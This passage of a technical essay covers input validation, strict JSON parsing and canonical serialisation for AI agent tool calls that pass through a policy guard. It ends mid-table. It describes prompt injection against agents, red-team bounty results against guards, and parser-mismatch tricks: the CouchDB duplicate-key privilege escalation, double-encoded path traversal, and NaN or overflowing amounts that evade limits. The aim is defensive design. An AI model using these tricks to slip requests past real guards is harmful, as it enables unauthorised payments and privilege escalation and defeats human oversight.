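# Input validation and canonical serialisation of AI agent requests before a policy decision

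## From an agent's request to a policy decision

An AI agent is a program in which a language model chooses actions. It can pay an invoice, delete a file or query a database by sending requests to other software. In many deployments, one component approves or refuses each request under a policy, and another carries out the approved requests. This check works only if both components interpret the request the same way. Input validation refuses requests that are malformed, ambiguous or outside what a tool accepts. Canonical serialisation writes each accepted request as one fixed string of bytes, so that software can recognise the same request when it arrives again. Both practices are older than AI agents and should come before the policy decision.

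### Tool calls, guards and executors

A tool call is a structured request from an agent, with a tool's name and its arguments. Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues (2026) describe its path in *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents*. The host, the software around the model, shows the model a list of tool definitions. The model emits a call, and the host executes it and returns the result to the model as text, which can influence the next call. They cite a count of 177,436 agent tools created between November 2024 and February 2026 in public repositories for the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for connecting models to tools. A growing share of those tools act on the world instead of only reading from it.

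Tool calls usually travel as JSON, a text format that writes data as pairs of names and values inside braces. A value can be a piece of text, a number, true or false, null, a list, or a further set of pairs. Take a company whose agent has to pay 1,250.50 euros to supplier S-204, under a policy that allows payments of up to 2,000 euros without a person's approval. The tool call might look like this:

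```
{"tool":"pay_supplier","arguments":{"supplier":"S-204","amount":1250.50,"currency":"EUR"}}
```

A schema is a machine-readable description of the fields, types and ranges that a tool accepts. For this tool, it could require a supplier number that matches a fixed pattern, a positive amount with at most two decimal places, and a currency from a short list. Any field the schema does not name is undeclared.

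The guard is the software or person that approves or refuses a tool call under a policy, and the executor is the component that carries out an approved call. *Before the Tool Call* (Uchibeke, 2026) makes the guard a blocking hook, so the agent framework calls it before every tool runs and waits for its answer. Because the hook is in the framework, a payment still has to pass the check even if some text has persuaded the model to request it. *If Agents Were Angels, No Governance Would Be Necessary* (Millstone, Akidau and colleagues, 2026) places the guard in a proxy between the agent and the systems it uses. A connector first translates each call into typed objects that specify who acts, what the action is, and on which resource and fields. The credential for the real system stays behind the proxy. In both designs, several programs handle a call between the model and the system that carries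 it out, and more than one of them may parse its text.

### Why agent output counts as attacker-controlled

A language model receives its instructions and the documents it reads in one stream of text, so it may follow instructions planted in an invoice or web page that the agent opens. Security engineers call this prompt injection. Whoever wrote the invoice can then influence the tool name, payee and amount in the agent's request, as well as the exact characters used to write them. For example, an attacker can ask for a number to be written in an unusual format as easily as for a different payee.

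A request can also be malformed without an attacker. A German invoice prints the example amount as 1.250,50, and a model may copy that text unchanged into the call. JavaScript's parseFloat function, which stops at the first character it cannot use, turns it into 1.25. If a guard parses amounts this way, it reads a payment of 12.500,00 as 12.5 and lets it pass the limit of 2,000. An executor whose library supports the German format then pays 12,500 euros.

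OWASP, a non-profit foundation that publishes security guidance, gives its plainest advice on validating model output in *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling*, an entry in the previous edition of its Top 10 for applications built on large language models (LLMs): "Treat the model as any other user", and validate whatever the model sends to backend functions. The current edition, issued on 3 August 2026 (OWASP, 2026), keeps the category and widens its scope but moves it from fifth place to tenth, according to Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026). On prompt injection, OWASP advises assuming that someone will eventually get past the model's instruction boundary and limiting what the model's output can reach, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents*.

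For the 2026 edition, OWASP also compared its members' votes with 7,714 recorded incidents, of which 6,639 had enough detail to classify. Voters ranked prompt injection first, but by raw incident count it would have dropped out of the top ten. They ranked misinformation, OWASP's heading for confident but wrong output, near the bottom, though it was near the top by incident count. OWASP attributes the gap for prompt injection to security teams' efforts to stop it. That may well be right, but a count drawn from public databases cannot distinguish an attack that is rarely attempted from one that is usually stopped.

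A guard can be designed without knowing which cause is more common. Millstone and colleagues treat the agent as untrusted and assume that it may propose any call and any arguments it can express, whether because of an attack, a model failure or the ordinary pursuit of its task. Their guarantees do not depend on which of these led to the call. They ran 3,621 benchmark trials against mock versions of two business systems. They counted a failure when protected data reached the agent or its answer, or when a forbidden action completed. In the main comparison, the failure rate fell from 57.6% for agents with only a prompt to 0.2% for agents behind the proxy, but the share of tasks fulfilled also fell, from 79.1% to 60.9%.

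Uchibeke, whose company develops the guard he tested, reports a live trial with a $5,000 bounty. Attackers persuaded the model to take the forbidden action 74.6% of the time under a permissive policy, while none of 879 attempts succeeded under a restrictive one. His list of attack methods includes manipulating parameters within a capability that the agent legitimately holds, such as altering the amount passed to a payment tool.

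These results are good evidence for putting the guard outside the model, but weaker evidence on whether the guard and the executor interpret a call the same way, because both designs largely assume that they do. Millstone and colleagues trust the connector and require the system behind it to execute the request as the connector interpreted it. Uchibeke assumes that the framework calls the guard, that the policy engine is deterministic and that the signing keys are safe, but none of these assumptions covers a tool that interprets an argument differently from the guard.

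### The steps before the decision

A careful design processes each call in nine steps, in a fixed order: limit size and depth, decode, parse, check against the schema, normalise, serialise canonically, hash, make the policy decision, and execute.

Size and depth limits come first because every later step uses time and memory. The receiving program counts the bytes and refuses a request above a set size. The parser also counts nesting levels as it reads and stops at a set maximum depth. It needs this second limit because JSON allows lists to be nested without end, and a parser that calls itself once per level can run out of memory on even a short text made of opening brackets.

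Decoding turns bytes into characters, nearly always under the UTF-8 standard. A strict decoder rejects byte sequences that the standard forbids. Some lax decoders used to accept a forbidden two-byte encoding of the slash, which attackers used to get file paths past filters that checked only for the usual one-byte form. Backslash Security, in guidance keyed to the public CWE catalogue of software weaknesses, tells developers to decode input to the application's internal representation before validating it, and never to decode the same input twice. For example, a filter that searches for two dots, the sign for a parent directory, finds none in `%252e%252e`. One round of URL decoding gives `%2e%2e`, which still contains no literal dots, and a second gives `..`. STIG Viewer's *The application must protect from canonical representation vulnerabilities* (2025), a requirement for US defence software,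 describes the general fault as code that expects data in one form but runs on data in another.

Next, the parser turns the characters into an object with fields. Strict parsing means accepting only input that matches a fixed grammar and schema, and rejecting the rest without repair. For example, the parser rejects an amount with a thousands comma, a name that occurs twice in one object, or stray text after the closing brace. If two components repair the same text differently, the result is parser disagreement, where they read the same bytes as different requests.

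The schema check then compares the object with what the tool accepts, and it rejects only what the schema rules out. Uchibeke gives an example for refunds in JSON Schema, a common language for writing schemas. The example requires a numeric amount and text fields for the currency and reason code, and one of its rules denies any refund above a limit. JSON Schema accepts undeclared fields unless the schema forbids them, and this one does not. It also sets no minimum amount, so a refund of minus 500 dollars satisfies both the schema and the limit. The paper's example may not match what the company deploys, but a production schema would have to close both gaps.

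Normalisation rewrites different accepted spellings of a request into one. In the payment example, the program converts the amount to a whole number of cents, so 1250.5 and 1250.50 both become 125050. This step needs the schema, which specifies that the field holds money with two decimals. The usual advice to canonicalise before validating is consistent with this order, because "canonicalise" there refers to the decoding that has already taken place. The program runs any test that depends on a value, such as the limit of 2,000 euros, after normalisation.

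Canonical serialisation writes the normalised request out again under fixed rules, for instance with fields in alphabetical order and no spaces:

```
{"arguments":{"amount_cents":125050,"currency":"EUR","supplier":"S-204"},"tool":"pay_supplier"}
```

This single byte string is the canonical form of the request and of every request that counts as equivalent to it. Its hash is a short value that can serve as the request identity in approvals, limits, logs and duplicate checks.

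The guard decides only at this point. It compares 125,050 cents with the limit of 200,000 and approves the payment without asking a person. For a sum above the limit, it would hold the call and wait for approval. Millstone and colleagues require any system that later resumes a held call to bind the approval to every part of the call that matters to the policy. A request identity gives the system something exact to bind the approval to.

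The executor, which runs last, works from the canonical bytes. If it used the agent's original text instead, it would parse that text again with different code and might make a different payment from the one the guard approved.

### Digests and signatures

A cryptographic hash function turns bytes of any length into a short, fixed-length value called a digest. The widely used SHA-256 produces a 32-byte digest. The same input always gives the same digest, but adding a single space gives one with no visible relation to the first. Nobody has published two different inputs with the same SHA-256 digest, so programs treat equal digests as proof of equal bytes. The holder of a private key computes a digital signature over some bytes, and anyone with the matching public key can check that the private key signed exactly those bytes. In Uchibeke's system, each agent has a "passport" that lists its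 capabilities and spending limits and carries a SHA-256 digest and an Ed25519 signature. The guard also signs a log entry for each decision, recording the agent, tool, parameters, outcome and time. Digests and signatures depend only on bytes, so a valid signature on a request with two readings shows which key signed it but does not settle which reading is correct.

### One payment in three spellings

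Each of the following lines asks for the same payment:

```
{"tool":"pay_supplier","arguments":{"supplier":"S-204","amount":1250.50,"currency":"EUR"}}
{"tool":"pay_supplier","arguments":{"currency":"EUR","amount":1250.5,"supplier":"S-204"}}
{"tool":"pay_supplier","arguments":{"supplier":"S-\u003204","amount":1.2505e3,"currency":"EUR"}}
```

The second line reorders the fields and drops a zero. The third writes the amount with an exponent and replaces the first digit of the supplier number with a character code, `\u0032`, which JSON allows. An ordinary JSON parser produces the same supplier, amount and currency from all three, but the digests of the raw texts are unrelated.

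Suppose the duplicate check compares digests of the raw text. The agent sends the first line, the connection times out, and the host asks the model to try again. The model happens to spell the call the second way, then the third way after another timeout. The check finds no match, and the executor pays 3,751.50 euros against a debt of 1,250.50. Each payment is below 2,000 euros, so no person sees them. An attacker who can steer the agent can ask for the respelling without waiting for a timeout.

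A spending limit can also fail in the opposite direction, by refusing payments that the policy permits. Policies often cap total spending as well as each payment. Uchibeke's sample passport, for example, allows 5,000 dollars per transaction and 25,000 per day. If the bank recognises the retries and pays once but the guard counts three requests, the guard's running total is 3,751.50 euros when only 1,250.50 has left the account, so the guard reaches the daily cap too early.

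Uchibeke requires determinism, meaning that the same inputs always produce the same decision. A guard that compares raw text can meet this requirement and still approve all three lines, because it treats them as three different inputs.

### Two properties of a canonical form

A canonical form has to satisfy two conditions. Equivalent requests must give the same canonical bytes, and requests that differ in effect must give different bytes. Write c for the function that takes a request, once it has passed the parser and the schema check, to its canonical bytes. Then for any two requests r1 and r2:

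c(r1) = c(r2) exactly when r1 and r2 are equivalent.

Either condition is easy to meet alone. A function that returns an empty string for every request gives equivalent requests the same bytes, but it gives all other requests those bytes too. A function that keeps the agent's spelling unchanged never merges two different payments, but it also treats the three lines above as different requests. Treating one request as several leads to double payments and wrong totals, while treating several requests as one lets an approval for one action cover another. For example, if the canonical form left out the supplier, a person's approval of a large payment to S-204 would also cover a payment of the same amount to anyone else.

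The formula does not define "equivalent", so someone has to define it for each tool. JSON's general rules establish that field order does not matter, but not whether `s-204` names the same supplier as `S-204`, or whether a request without a currency equals one in euros because the tool assumes euros. The tool's owner knows what the executor does with each field, and the policy's owner knows which differences matter to an approval. Millstone and colleagues run into the same limit with their connector. If its mapping leaves out a field that the policy depends on, their guarantees no longer cover that path, and the operator must block it or govern it by other means.

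Equivalence between requests must be transitive, because equality of byte strings is. If r1 is equivalent to r2, and r2 to r3, then r1 must be equivalent to r3. The rule "amounts within one cent of each other are equal" sounds reasonable but breaks this condition. It makes 1,250.50 equal to 1,250.51 and 1,250.51 equal to 1,250.52, but not 1,250.50 equal to 1,250.52, so no function c can satisfy it. Rounding every amount to a whole euro gives a consistent rule, but it can merge payments that differ by cents.

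The definition also determines what the schema must contain. Supplier S-204 may send two genuine invoices for 1,250.50 euros in the same month. If a request contains only the supplier, amount and currency, both payments have the same canonical form and the duplicate check blocks the second. If the schema also requires an invoice number, the check detects a retry because it has the same number as the original request, while the second invoice has a new number and goes through.

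## A repeated key read two ways: the CouchDB flaw of 2017

Apache CouchDB is a database that stores its records as JSON documents. On 14 November 2017 its developers disclosed a flaw, CVE-2017-12635, that let ordinary users make themselves administrators. One component checked a user record and another used it, and the two resolved a repeated key differently. The flaw is older than tool-calling agents, but CouchDB divided its work much as a guard and an executor do.

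### One record with two sets of roles

Most of CouchDB is written in Erlang, but database administrators can add validation scripts in JavaScript, which CouchDB runs whenever someone creates or changes a document. Max Justicz, who found the flaw, explains in *Remote Code Execution in CouchDB* (2017) how this worked for user accounts. CouchDB stores each account as a document with a field called `roles`, and a validation script was meant to stop users from assigning roles to themselves. The Erlang code parsed the submitted document, wrote it out again as JSON and sent it to the script, which ran in a separate process.

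An attacker could submit a user record in which `roles` appeared twice with different values. JavaScript's parser keeps only the last value of a repeated name, so the validation script checked the second `roles` field. The Erlang parser kept both values, and the function that looked up a field in the parsed record returned the first. Apache CouchDB's official advisory, *CVE-2017-12635* (2017), confirms that the second field determined whether CouchDB accepted the record and the first determined what the new user could do. An attacker could therefore create an administrator account by putting the administrator role in the first field and no special rights in the second.

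The flaw affected every version of CouchDB, and OSV's *CVE-2017-12635* (2017) lists its severity as 9.8 out of 10. An attacker who combined it with a second flaw could run commands on the server. Justicz first wrote that the flaw also exposed npm, the main registry of JavaScript packages, to tampering. He withdrew the claim after learning that the registry had used its own login system since early 2015.

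The validation script, which acted as the guard, did not check the request that the executor carried out. Hashing or signing the submitted document would not have exposed this, because both components started from the same bytes. CouchDB serialised the record again before the check, but the parsed record still held both values, so the new text also repeated the key. Serialisation removes an ambiguity only if the parser has already refused or resolved it. A person reviewing the account would have missed the problem too, because the administration screen also parsed the record in JavaScript and showed an empty list of roles.

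The developers fixed the flaw by making the Erlang parser take the last value, as JavaScript does. They could have rejected documents with repeated names instead, but matching JavaScript was probably less disruptive, since CouchDB could still accept those documents and the developers promised smooth upgrades within each version series. The fix removed only the difference that Justicz had found. The two parsers, and any other program that read the same documents, still had to agree on every other ambiguous input. Justicz advises developers to avoid using more than one parser on the same data and, where they can't, to make sure that the parsers behave alike. Rejecting repeated names is safer than making the parsers match, because a document that the first parser rejects never reaches the second.

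### Why both parsers followed the rules

Neither parser broke the general JSON standard. Its current version, *The JavaScript Object Notation (JSON) Data Interchange Format* (RFC 8259; Bray, 2017), states that the names within an object "SHOULD be unique". In internet standards, SHOULD marks a recommendation that implementers may set aside for good reason, unlike MUST, which marks a requirement. Bray calls the behaviour of software that receives repeated names "unpredictable". Many implementations report only the last value, others report an error or fail to parse the object, and some report every value. CouchDB's two parsers behaved in two of these ways.

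The JavaScript parser followed a firmer rule, set by the JavaScript standard of the time, that a later value overwrites an earlier one with the same name. Bray's blog post *JSON Lesson* (2013) quotes the rule.

The word SHOULD goes back to the first JSON standard, which Douglas Crockford wrote in 2006. During a debate among Erlang developers about repeated keys, one of them asked Crockford about the word, and O'Keefe (2011), in *JSON*, relays his answer: "The RFC SHOULD have said MUST." O'Keefe concluded that JSON data should never contain repeated keys, so how a parser handled them should not matter much. That is reasonable if every sender is honest, but an attacker can repeat keys on purpose, as the CouchDB case showed six years later.

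By 2013 Crockford thought it was too late to change the statement that names in a JSON object SHOULD be unique to MUST. In *JSON Duplicate Keys*, Crockford (2013) proposed instead that a parser should reject a repeated name and, if it did not, must take the last value. RFC 8259 does not include this rule, which CouchDB's Erlang code would have broken. ECMA-404, a parallel specification, does not even recommend unique names. In October 2025 a reader reported this as a contradiction between the two documents, and a reviewer rejected the report the next day (RFC Editor, *RFC Errata*, 2025).

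RFC 8259 also requires a parser to accept every text that fits the JSON grammar, which allows repeated names. A parser that rejects them therefore appears to break this rule, although Bray lists rejection among the existing behaviours without objecting to it. *The I-JSON Message Format* (RFC 7493; Bray, 2015) avoids this conflict by defining a restricted version of JSON in which names MUST NOT repeat. I-JSON also requires UTF-8 and forbids character codes that do not stand for characters. Receivers may reject any message that breaks these rules, and a protocol built on I-JSON can require them to. Bray adds that such a protocol should let the receiver tell the sender what was wrong.

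His advice on undeclared fields suits a guard less well. He recommends that receivers ignore fields they do not recognise, so that a protocol can gain fields without breaking old software. But a guard that ignores a field the executor recognises has not checked the whole request.

### The rules of a strict parser

Programming languages have begun to adopt stricter defaults. Go, a language common in server software, added a new JSON package, encoding/json/v2, to its standard library in version 1.27 (Go release notes, August 2026). *A new experimental Go API for JSON* (Tsai, Martí and colleagues, 2025) cites the CouchDB flaw as a reason for one of the changes. It adds that JSON parsers in general have become stricter, which makes it less likely that two of them will accept the same text but interpret it differently.

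A strict parser rejects any object that contains the same name twice, at any depth of nesting. It decodes escape sequences before comparing names, because `amount` and `\u0061mount` are the same name in JSON. If it compared the raw spellings, it would pass the duplicate to a program that decodes them later. Go's old JSON package accepts repeated names, while the new one reports an error.

Names that differ only in case can cause a similar problem. JSON treats `amount` and `Amount` as different names, but Go's old package ignores case when it matches names to a program's fields. Suppose a call contains an `amount` of 900 followed by an `Amount` of 9,000. A guard that matches names exactly reads 900 and treats `Amount` as an undeclared field. If the guard ignores that field and the executor uses the old Go package, the second value overwrites the first and the executor pays 9,000. A strict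 parser matches names exactly and refuses an object in which two names differ only in case. According to Go's documentation, the new package matches names exactly but still ignores undeclared fields by default, so a guard that uses it needs the option to reject them.

Invalid Unicode can make two different requests look the same. The old package silently replaces bytes that are not valid UTF-8 with a standard replacement character. Two file names that differ only in their invalid bytes then become equal, and an approval to delete one file would also cover the other. The new package reports an error instead. JSON escape codes represent some characters, such as emoji, as a pair of codes called surrogates, and half a pair does not represent any character. Bray notes that software can produce half a pair by cutting a text in the middle of one, and that programs may then compute different lengths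 for the text or even crash. I-JSON forbids these half pairs, and a strict parser should reject them too.

The parser must also read to the end of the input and reject anything but white space after the closing brace. Tsai and colleagues describe a common mistake in Go, where programmers use a function that reads one JSON value from a stream and leaves the rest unread. If a guard does this and the text contains two tool calls in a row, the guard checks only the first call, but an executor that processes the whole stream runs both.

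NaN ("not a number") is the floating-point result of an undefined operation such as zero divided by zero. It is neither greater nor less than any number, so a policy that refuses payments greater than 2,000 lets NaN through. RFC 8259 excludes NaN and infinity from JSON but allows parsers to accept extensions, and Python's standard parser accepts both by default. Parsers can also produce infinity from valid JSON numbers. The text `-1E400` fits the JSON grammar but is too large in magnitude for the usual 64-bit floating-point format, so many parsers turn it into negative infinity, which is below every spending limit. A strict parser rejects NaN and infinity when they are written by name, and checks that each number is finite after conversion.

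Large whole numbers can change without warning. The same floating-point format represents every whole number exactly only up to 2^53 − 1 (9,007,199,254,740,991), and beyond that it skips some. JavaScript's parser turns 9007199254740993 into 9007199254740992. If those are account numbers, a guard in JavaScript checks the permissions of one account while an executor with exact integers changes another. A strict parser rejects integers outside the safe range, and a tool that needs larger ones should declare the field as a string of digits. I-JSON recommends this, and Go's package has a setting for it. Decimal amounts need an even stricter grammar.

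RFC 8259 lets implementations limit the size of a JSON text, its nesting depth, the range of its numbers and the length of its strings. A parser that reaches a limit must refuse the request rather than truncate it. If a guard reads only the first megabyte of a longer request, it can approve the request without checking the rest.

Upgrading Go does not make an existing guard strict, because the old package keeps its behaviour and programmers have to switch to the new one themselves. Go's *encoding/json/v2 Migration Guide* explains that some applications may depend on the old behaviour. For large services, it suggests a tool that runs both packages in production, reports any differences and still returns the old result. This roughly doubles the computation for each conversion, so programmers can set the tool to check only a sample. They can also turn off the new package's strict rules one at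 a time, so the package's name alone does not show how strict a guard is.

### Tolerance, refusal and retry

Many engineers learned the opposite habit from the robustness principle of Jon Postel, who edited early internet standards: "be conservative in what you send, and liberal in what you accept". This made sense for a network of programs by many authors. Specifications had gaps, senders made small mistakes, and whoever ran the receiving program usually could not get the sender's code fixed. If every program had refused every imperfect message, much of the network would not have worked.

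Software around language models often follows the same principle. It removes a sentence the model wrote before its JSON, adds a missing brace, or converts the text "1250.50" into a number because the tool expects one. Developers have a good reason to do this, since the intended call is usually clear from the text and refusing it over a stray comma may make a task fail that was otherwise going well.

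Len Sassaman, Meredith Patterson and Sergey Bratus developed an opposing view they call language-theoretic security. They treat a program's valid inputs as a formal language, a set of texts that a grammar defines exactly. They say a program should check that the entire input belongs to this language before acting on any part of it. They also want input formats to be simple. For some simple classes of grammar, an algorithm can determine whether two grammars define the same set of texts, but no algorithm can do so for all context-free grammars, the class that programming languages mostly use for their syntax. Testing can find differences between two complicated parsers, but it cannot prove that none remain.

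Barenghi, Mainardi and Pelosi (2018), in *Systematic Parsing of X.509*, applied this approach to the certificates that websites use to prove their identity. They wrote a grammar for the format, generated a parser from it and ran the parser on 11 million certificates from web servers. The parser rejected 21.5% as syntactically invalid. Seven widely used libraries each accepted between 631,000 and 1,156,000 of these, or 5.7% to 10.5% of the collection.

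The most tolerant library therefore accepted at least 525,000 certificates that the least tolerant one refused, so parser disagreement was common even in software built for security. Defenders of tolerance also have a point, because the most tolerant library would have rejected about a tenth of the certificates in the collection if it had suddenly adopted the strict grammar. JSON libraries also disagree, though the evidence is less detailed. Zhong, Cao and Zhang (2024), in *Large Language Models Based JSON Parser Fuzzing for Bug Discovery*, cite a 2021 comparison of Java libraries by Harrand and colleagues, which found wide differences in how the libraries handled malformed files, large numbers and duplicate data.

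In *Maintaining Robust Protocols* (RFC 9413), an Internet Architecture Board document, Thomson and Schinazi (2023) reconsider Postel's principle. The draft behind it replaced one named "postel-was-wrong", but the published text is milder. Thomson and Schinazi accept that some interpretations of the principle help the internet but warn against applying it too broadly. They want people to keep maintaining protocols by correcting both specifications and software to reduce ambiguity over time. Tolerance works against this because a receiver that silently fixes a mistake hides it from the person who could correct the sender.

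The sender of a tool call can correct the mistake within seconds. The host returns an error naming the faulty field, and the model writes the call again. This weakens the practical case for tolerance, which was strongest when nobody could reach the sender in time. A refused call has not run, so retrying it is also safer than retrying after a timeout, when the call may have run.

*Gecko* (Zhang, Li and colleagues, 2026) gives some idea of how useful returned errors are. It describes a simulated environment in which a model can try out tool calls before using the real tools. The environment rejects unknown tools, missing or unsupported arguments and wrong types, and returns an error message for each. A second language model looks for values that have the right type but the wrong meaning, such as a company's name where the tool expects its stock symbol. Gecko then simulates the tool's response,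 tracks the state of the task and reports what remains to be done.

On a set of tasks that take several rounds of conversation, Gecko raised the accuracy of GPT-4o, a 2024 model, from 61.0% to 72.0%. Accuracy was 70.5% without the argument checks and 61.5% without the feedback on whether the task was complete, so the feedback helped far more. Zhang and colleagues removed the checks on format and meaning together, so the 1.5-point drop without argument checks does not measure the effect of format errors alone.

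They also varied the number of retries on a set of simple single-call tasks. Accuracy rose from 92.25% with no retry to 96.50% with up to three, and most of the gain came from the first. Average time per task rose from 7.5 to 18.1 seconds, and average cost rose from about 1.0 to 2.6 US cents. These retries used all of Gecko's feedback, so only part of the gain can come from fixing format errors. The experiment does not test automatic repair of broken JSON, so it cannot show whether repair or retry completes more tasks. It suggests that a model can make good use of an error message and that a host can get most of the benefit with a limit of one retry.

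Repairing a request's text does not harm the policy decision if one component makes the repair before the guard sees the text, and the executor carries out the same repaired object that the guard judged. The strict parser and the schema check run after the repair, the digest covers the repaired request, and the original text is kept only in a log. A repair at this stage, such as adding a missing brace, can change which request the model makes, but it cannot make the guard and the executor read different requests.

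Repair anywhere else is dangerous. If the guard repairs the text for its own use but passes on the original, the executor has to interpret the broken version itself. If the executor converts or completes values after the approval, it may carry out something the guard never checked. Using a separate repair library on each side is worse than using two ordinary parsers, because no standard defines what a repair should produce. Choosing one of two repeated values is also a kind of repair, and CouchDB's two components silently chose different ones.

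Even in the right position, repair can produce a request that nobody intended. Suppose an agent asks to delete files more than a year old from a folder, and the model reaches its output limit just before writing the age. A repair tool closes the open brace and produces a valid request to delete every file in the folder. The guard and the executor now read the same request, and if the policy lets the agent delete files there, the guard approves it. A host can safely remove text around a complete JSON object, but it should refuse an incomplete one and ask the model to write the call again.

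## Undeclared fields and repeated parsing in agent tools: a 2026 study

CouchDB read one record with two parsers. A tool call can pass through more than two. The model's provider turns the generated text into a call, gateways translate it between providers' formats, and the agent framework, the guard and the executor may each parse it again. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz (2026) showed in their November preprint, *Oops!... I Parsed It Again*, that a guard and an executor that parse the same bytes separately can act on different calls. They also surveyed the schemas of widely used tools and tested five defences against an attacker who knows how each one works.

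### Open and closed schemas

JSON Schema accepts undeclared fields by default because its keywords only add restrictions. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) proposal *Establish JSON Schema 2020-12 as default dialect* explains what this means for tools. An empty schema accepts any input, and a schema that requires only an object accepts an object with any fields.

A schema for the supplier payment might look like this:

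```
{"type":"object",
 "properties":{
   "supplier":{"type":"string"},
   "amount":{"type":"number"},
   "currency":{"type":"string"},
   "urgent":{"type":"boolean","default":false}},
 "required":["supplier","amount","currency"]}
```

A validator accepts a call that meets these rules even if it also contains `"pay_on":"2026-12-01"`, a field the schema does not declare. A schema that allows undeclared fields is open. The tool's owner can close it by adding `"additionalProperties": false`, and a validator then rejects the same call. The keyword applies only to the object that contains it, so a nested object, such as an address, needs its own.

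Closing a schema is harder when developers build it from parts. Suppose a company keeps its common payment fields in one closed schema, and one tool also needs an `invoice` field. The tool's schema can include the common part with `allOf`, which requires a request to satisfy every part listed. But `additionalProperties` only considers fields declared in the same part, as JSON Schema's tutorial *Extending Closed Schemas* explains, so the common part rejects any call that includes `invoice`. If the company removes the keyword from the common part, the whole schema accepts undeclared fields again.

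The 2019 version of JSON Schema added `unevaluatedProperties` to solve this problem. The validator applies all the parts first, records which fields they covered, and refuses any others:

```
{"allOf":[{"$ref":"#/$defs/payment"}],
 "properties":{"invoice":{"type":"string"}},
 "unevaluatedProperties":false}
```

`payment` refers to the common fields, whose definition must now be open. JSON Schema draft-07, an older version, lacks this keyword, and its validators often ignore unrecognised keywords. The same schema can then be closed for the guard and open for the executor, so a schema that relies on the keyword should state which version of JSON Schema it uses.

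### What deployed schemas accept

Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz collected the schemas of 5,778 tools from the 100 most-used MCP servers in the Smithery registry and six official reference servers. Every schema, as the registry served it, accepted undeclared fields at the top level. The gap in Uchibeke's refund example is therefore normal among popular tools.

A result of exactly 100% is slightly odd, because the MCP specification recommends a closed schema for tools without parameters, and some of the 5,778 tools probably take no parameters. Either all the developers of those tools didn't follow the recommendation, or the keyword that closes a schema was lost between the servers and the registry's listing. A guard that takes its schemas from the registry has the same problem in both cases, but an operator who takes them from the server should check whether they are open.

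The schemas are otherwise well formed. In *What a Random Draw from the MCP Registry Contains*, Afsar (2026) drew 400 servers at random from part of the official MCP registry and tried to start each one once. The 195 that started offered 2,766 tools, none of which had a fatal schema error, such as a missing schema or an invalid type. This is consistent with the survey, because an open schema is valid.

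Afsar's results also suggest that less popular servers may differ from the popular ones in the Smithery survey. Optional notes on whether a tool is read-only or destructive were missing from 58.8% of the tools in his random sample, compared with 41.5% in an earlier hand-picked one. On undeclared fields, however, less popular servers have little room to do worse than those in the survey.

An open schema is harmless if something removes the extra fields before the tool runs, as the official MCP libraries do. But Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz also read the source code of deployed gateways that pass on every field when they translate a call from one provider's format to another's. If a guard in front of such a gateway checks only the declared fields, the tool receives any extra fields unchecked.

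Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz also looked for schemas that components interpret differently. They ran 4,693 distinct schemas through two common validators, under both draft-07 and the 2020-12 version, and compared a call that left out fields with default values against the same call with the defaults filled in. For 558 schemas (11.9%), on 64 servers, components ended up with different arguments or verdicts.

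Most of these differences, 541 in all, occurred because the executor received different arguments depending on whether some component filled in the schema's defaults. The validators disagreed about whether a schema was valid in only the remaining 17 cases, even though almost none of the tools named a JSON Schema version.

### Defaults and omitted fields

In JSON Schema, `default` only describes a value, and a validator is not required to insert it. If a payment call leaves out `urgent`, most validators accept the call and leave the field absent, while other software fills in the default, `false`. Two components can therefore read the same text correctly and hold different objects. In the survey, 10.7% of tools declared at least one default, and 60.4% of servers had at least one such tool.

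Models omit optional fields from tool calls even without an attacker. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz asked six commercial models to call a tool that had an optional field with a default. Five of the six omitted the field in all 40 of their calls.

The omission can matter a great deal if the schema and the executor's code disagree. For example, a tool for deleting files might have an optional field `permanent` that defaults to false in the schema, while the executor's older code treats a missing field as true. A guard that fills in the default would approve moving the files to a recycle bin, but an executor that receives the agent's original text would delete them permanently. If the executor instead receives the completed request, which includes `permanent: false`, it does what the guard approved.

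Defaults also affect request identity. If `urgent` defaults to `false`, a payment request that omits it is equivalent to one that sets it to `false`, but the two have different digests unless normalisation fills in the default before serialisation. Filling in the default also means that if the tool's owner later changes it to `true`, a new call without the field gets a new digest, so an approval given before the change does not cover it.

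The guard should take its defaults from a copy of the schema that the operator has reviewed and stored. MCP servers supply their own schemas to clients, so a malicious or compromised server could change a default after the review.

### Five ways to keep the guard and the executor together

Three of the five defences leave the executor to parse the original bytes. The simplest is schema validation, in which the guard checks the arguments against the tool's schema before it decides. This guarantees acceptable fields and types only in the object the guard parsed. The executor may parse the same bytes into a different object, and both objects can satisfy the schema.

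A more demanding check is for the guard to read the bytes with two parsers and refuse the call if the results differ. This guarantees that those two parsers agree, so it protects the executor only if the executor reads the text the way one of them does. It also doesn't help if the guard searches the raw text for forbidden words instead of using the parsed values.

Some gateways parse a call once, check the result, and forward the original bytes. The executor still has to parse those bytes itself, so the guarantee again covers only the guard's own parse.

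A provider's strict output mode acts earlier, while the model is writing. In its *Structured Outputs* documentation, OpenAI promises that output in its strict mode will match the developer's schema. Developers must forbid undeclared fields in every object and make every declared field required. To make a field optional in practice, they allow null as a value, so the model must write either a real value or null. In the study, every call under OpenAI's strict mode was complete, and the disagreements over omitted fields disappeared.

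That guarantee applies only to the text as it leaves the provider, and a gateway can change the text afterwards. A provider also enforces whatever schema it receives, even one from a malicious tool server. OpenAI warns that a response may not match the schema if the model refuses to answer or reaches its length limit. The mode supports only part of JSON Schema, and in the study it rejected all 80 requests that used `oneOf`, a keyword for choosing between alternatives.

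Strict mode can also empty an argument that the developer meant to be free-form. In a *Bug Report* on OpenAI's forum, one developer complains that a model returned no filter for a product search when it should have returned a brand name. The schema in the report is enough to explain this, because it declares the filter as a closed object but lists no fields, so the only valid values are an empty object and null. The developer would have to declare the possible filters or ask for a list of names and values.

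Allowing null also complicates the canonical form. One provider's model may omit an optional field, another may write null, and a third may write the default. If the executor treats all three the same way, normalisation has to convert them to one value.

In the fifth defence, which Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz call a shared parse, one component reads the original bytes once. It keeps only the fields in the approved schema, at every level of nesting, and fills in the defaults. It also parses JSON inside string arguments that the operator has marked. The guard checks the resulting object, and the executor runs that same object.

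The study tested these defences with nine attempts, using inputs chosen to defeat each one, and with a larger set of 7,412 inputs. The table leaves out strict mode, which cannot control bytes that someone changes after the provider sends them.

| Defence | Attacks that succeeded, of 9 | Attacks that succeeded, of 7,412 |
|---|---|---|
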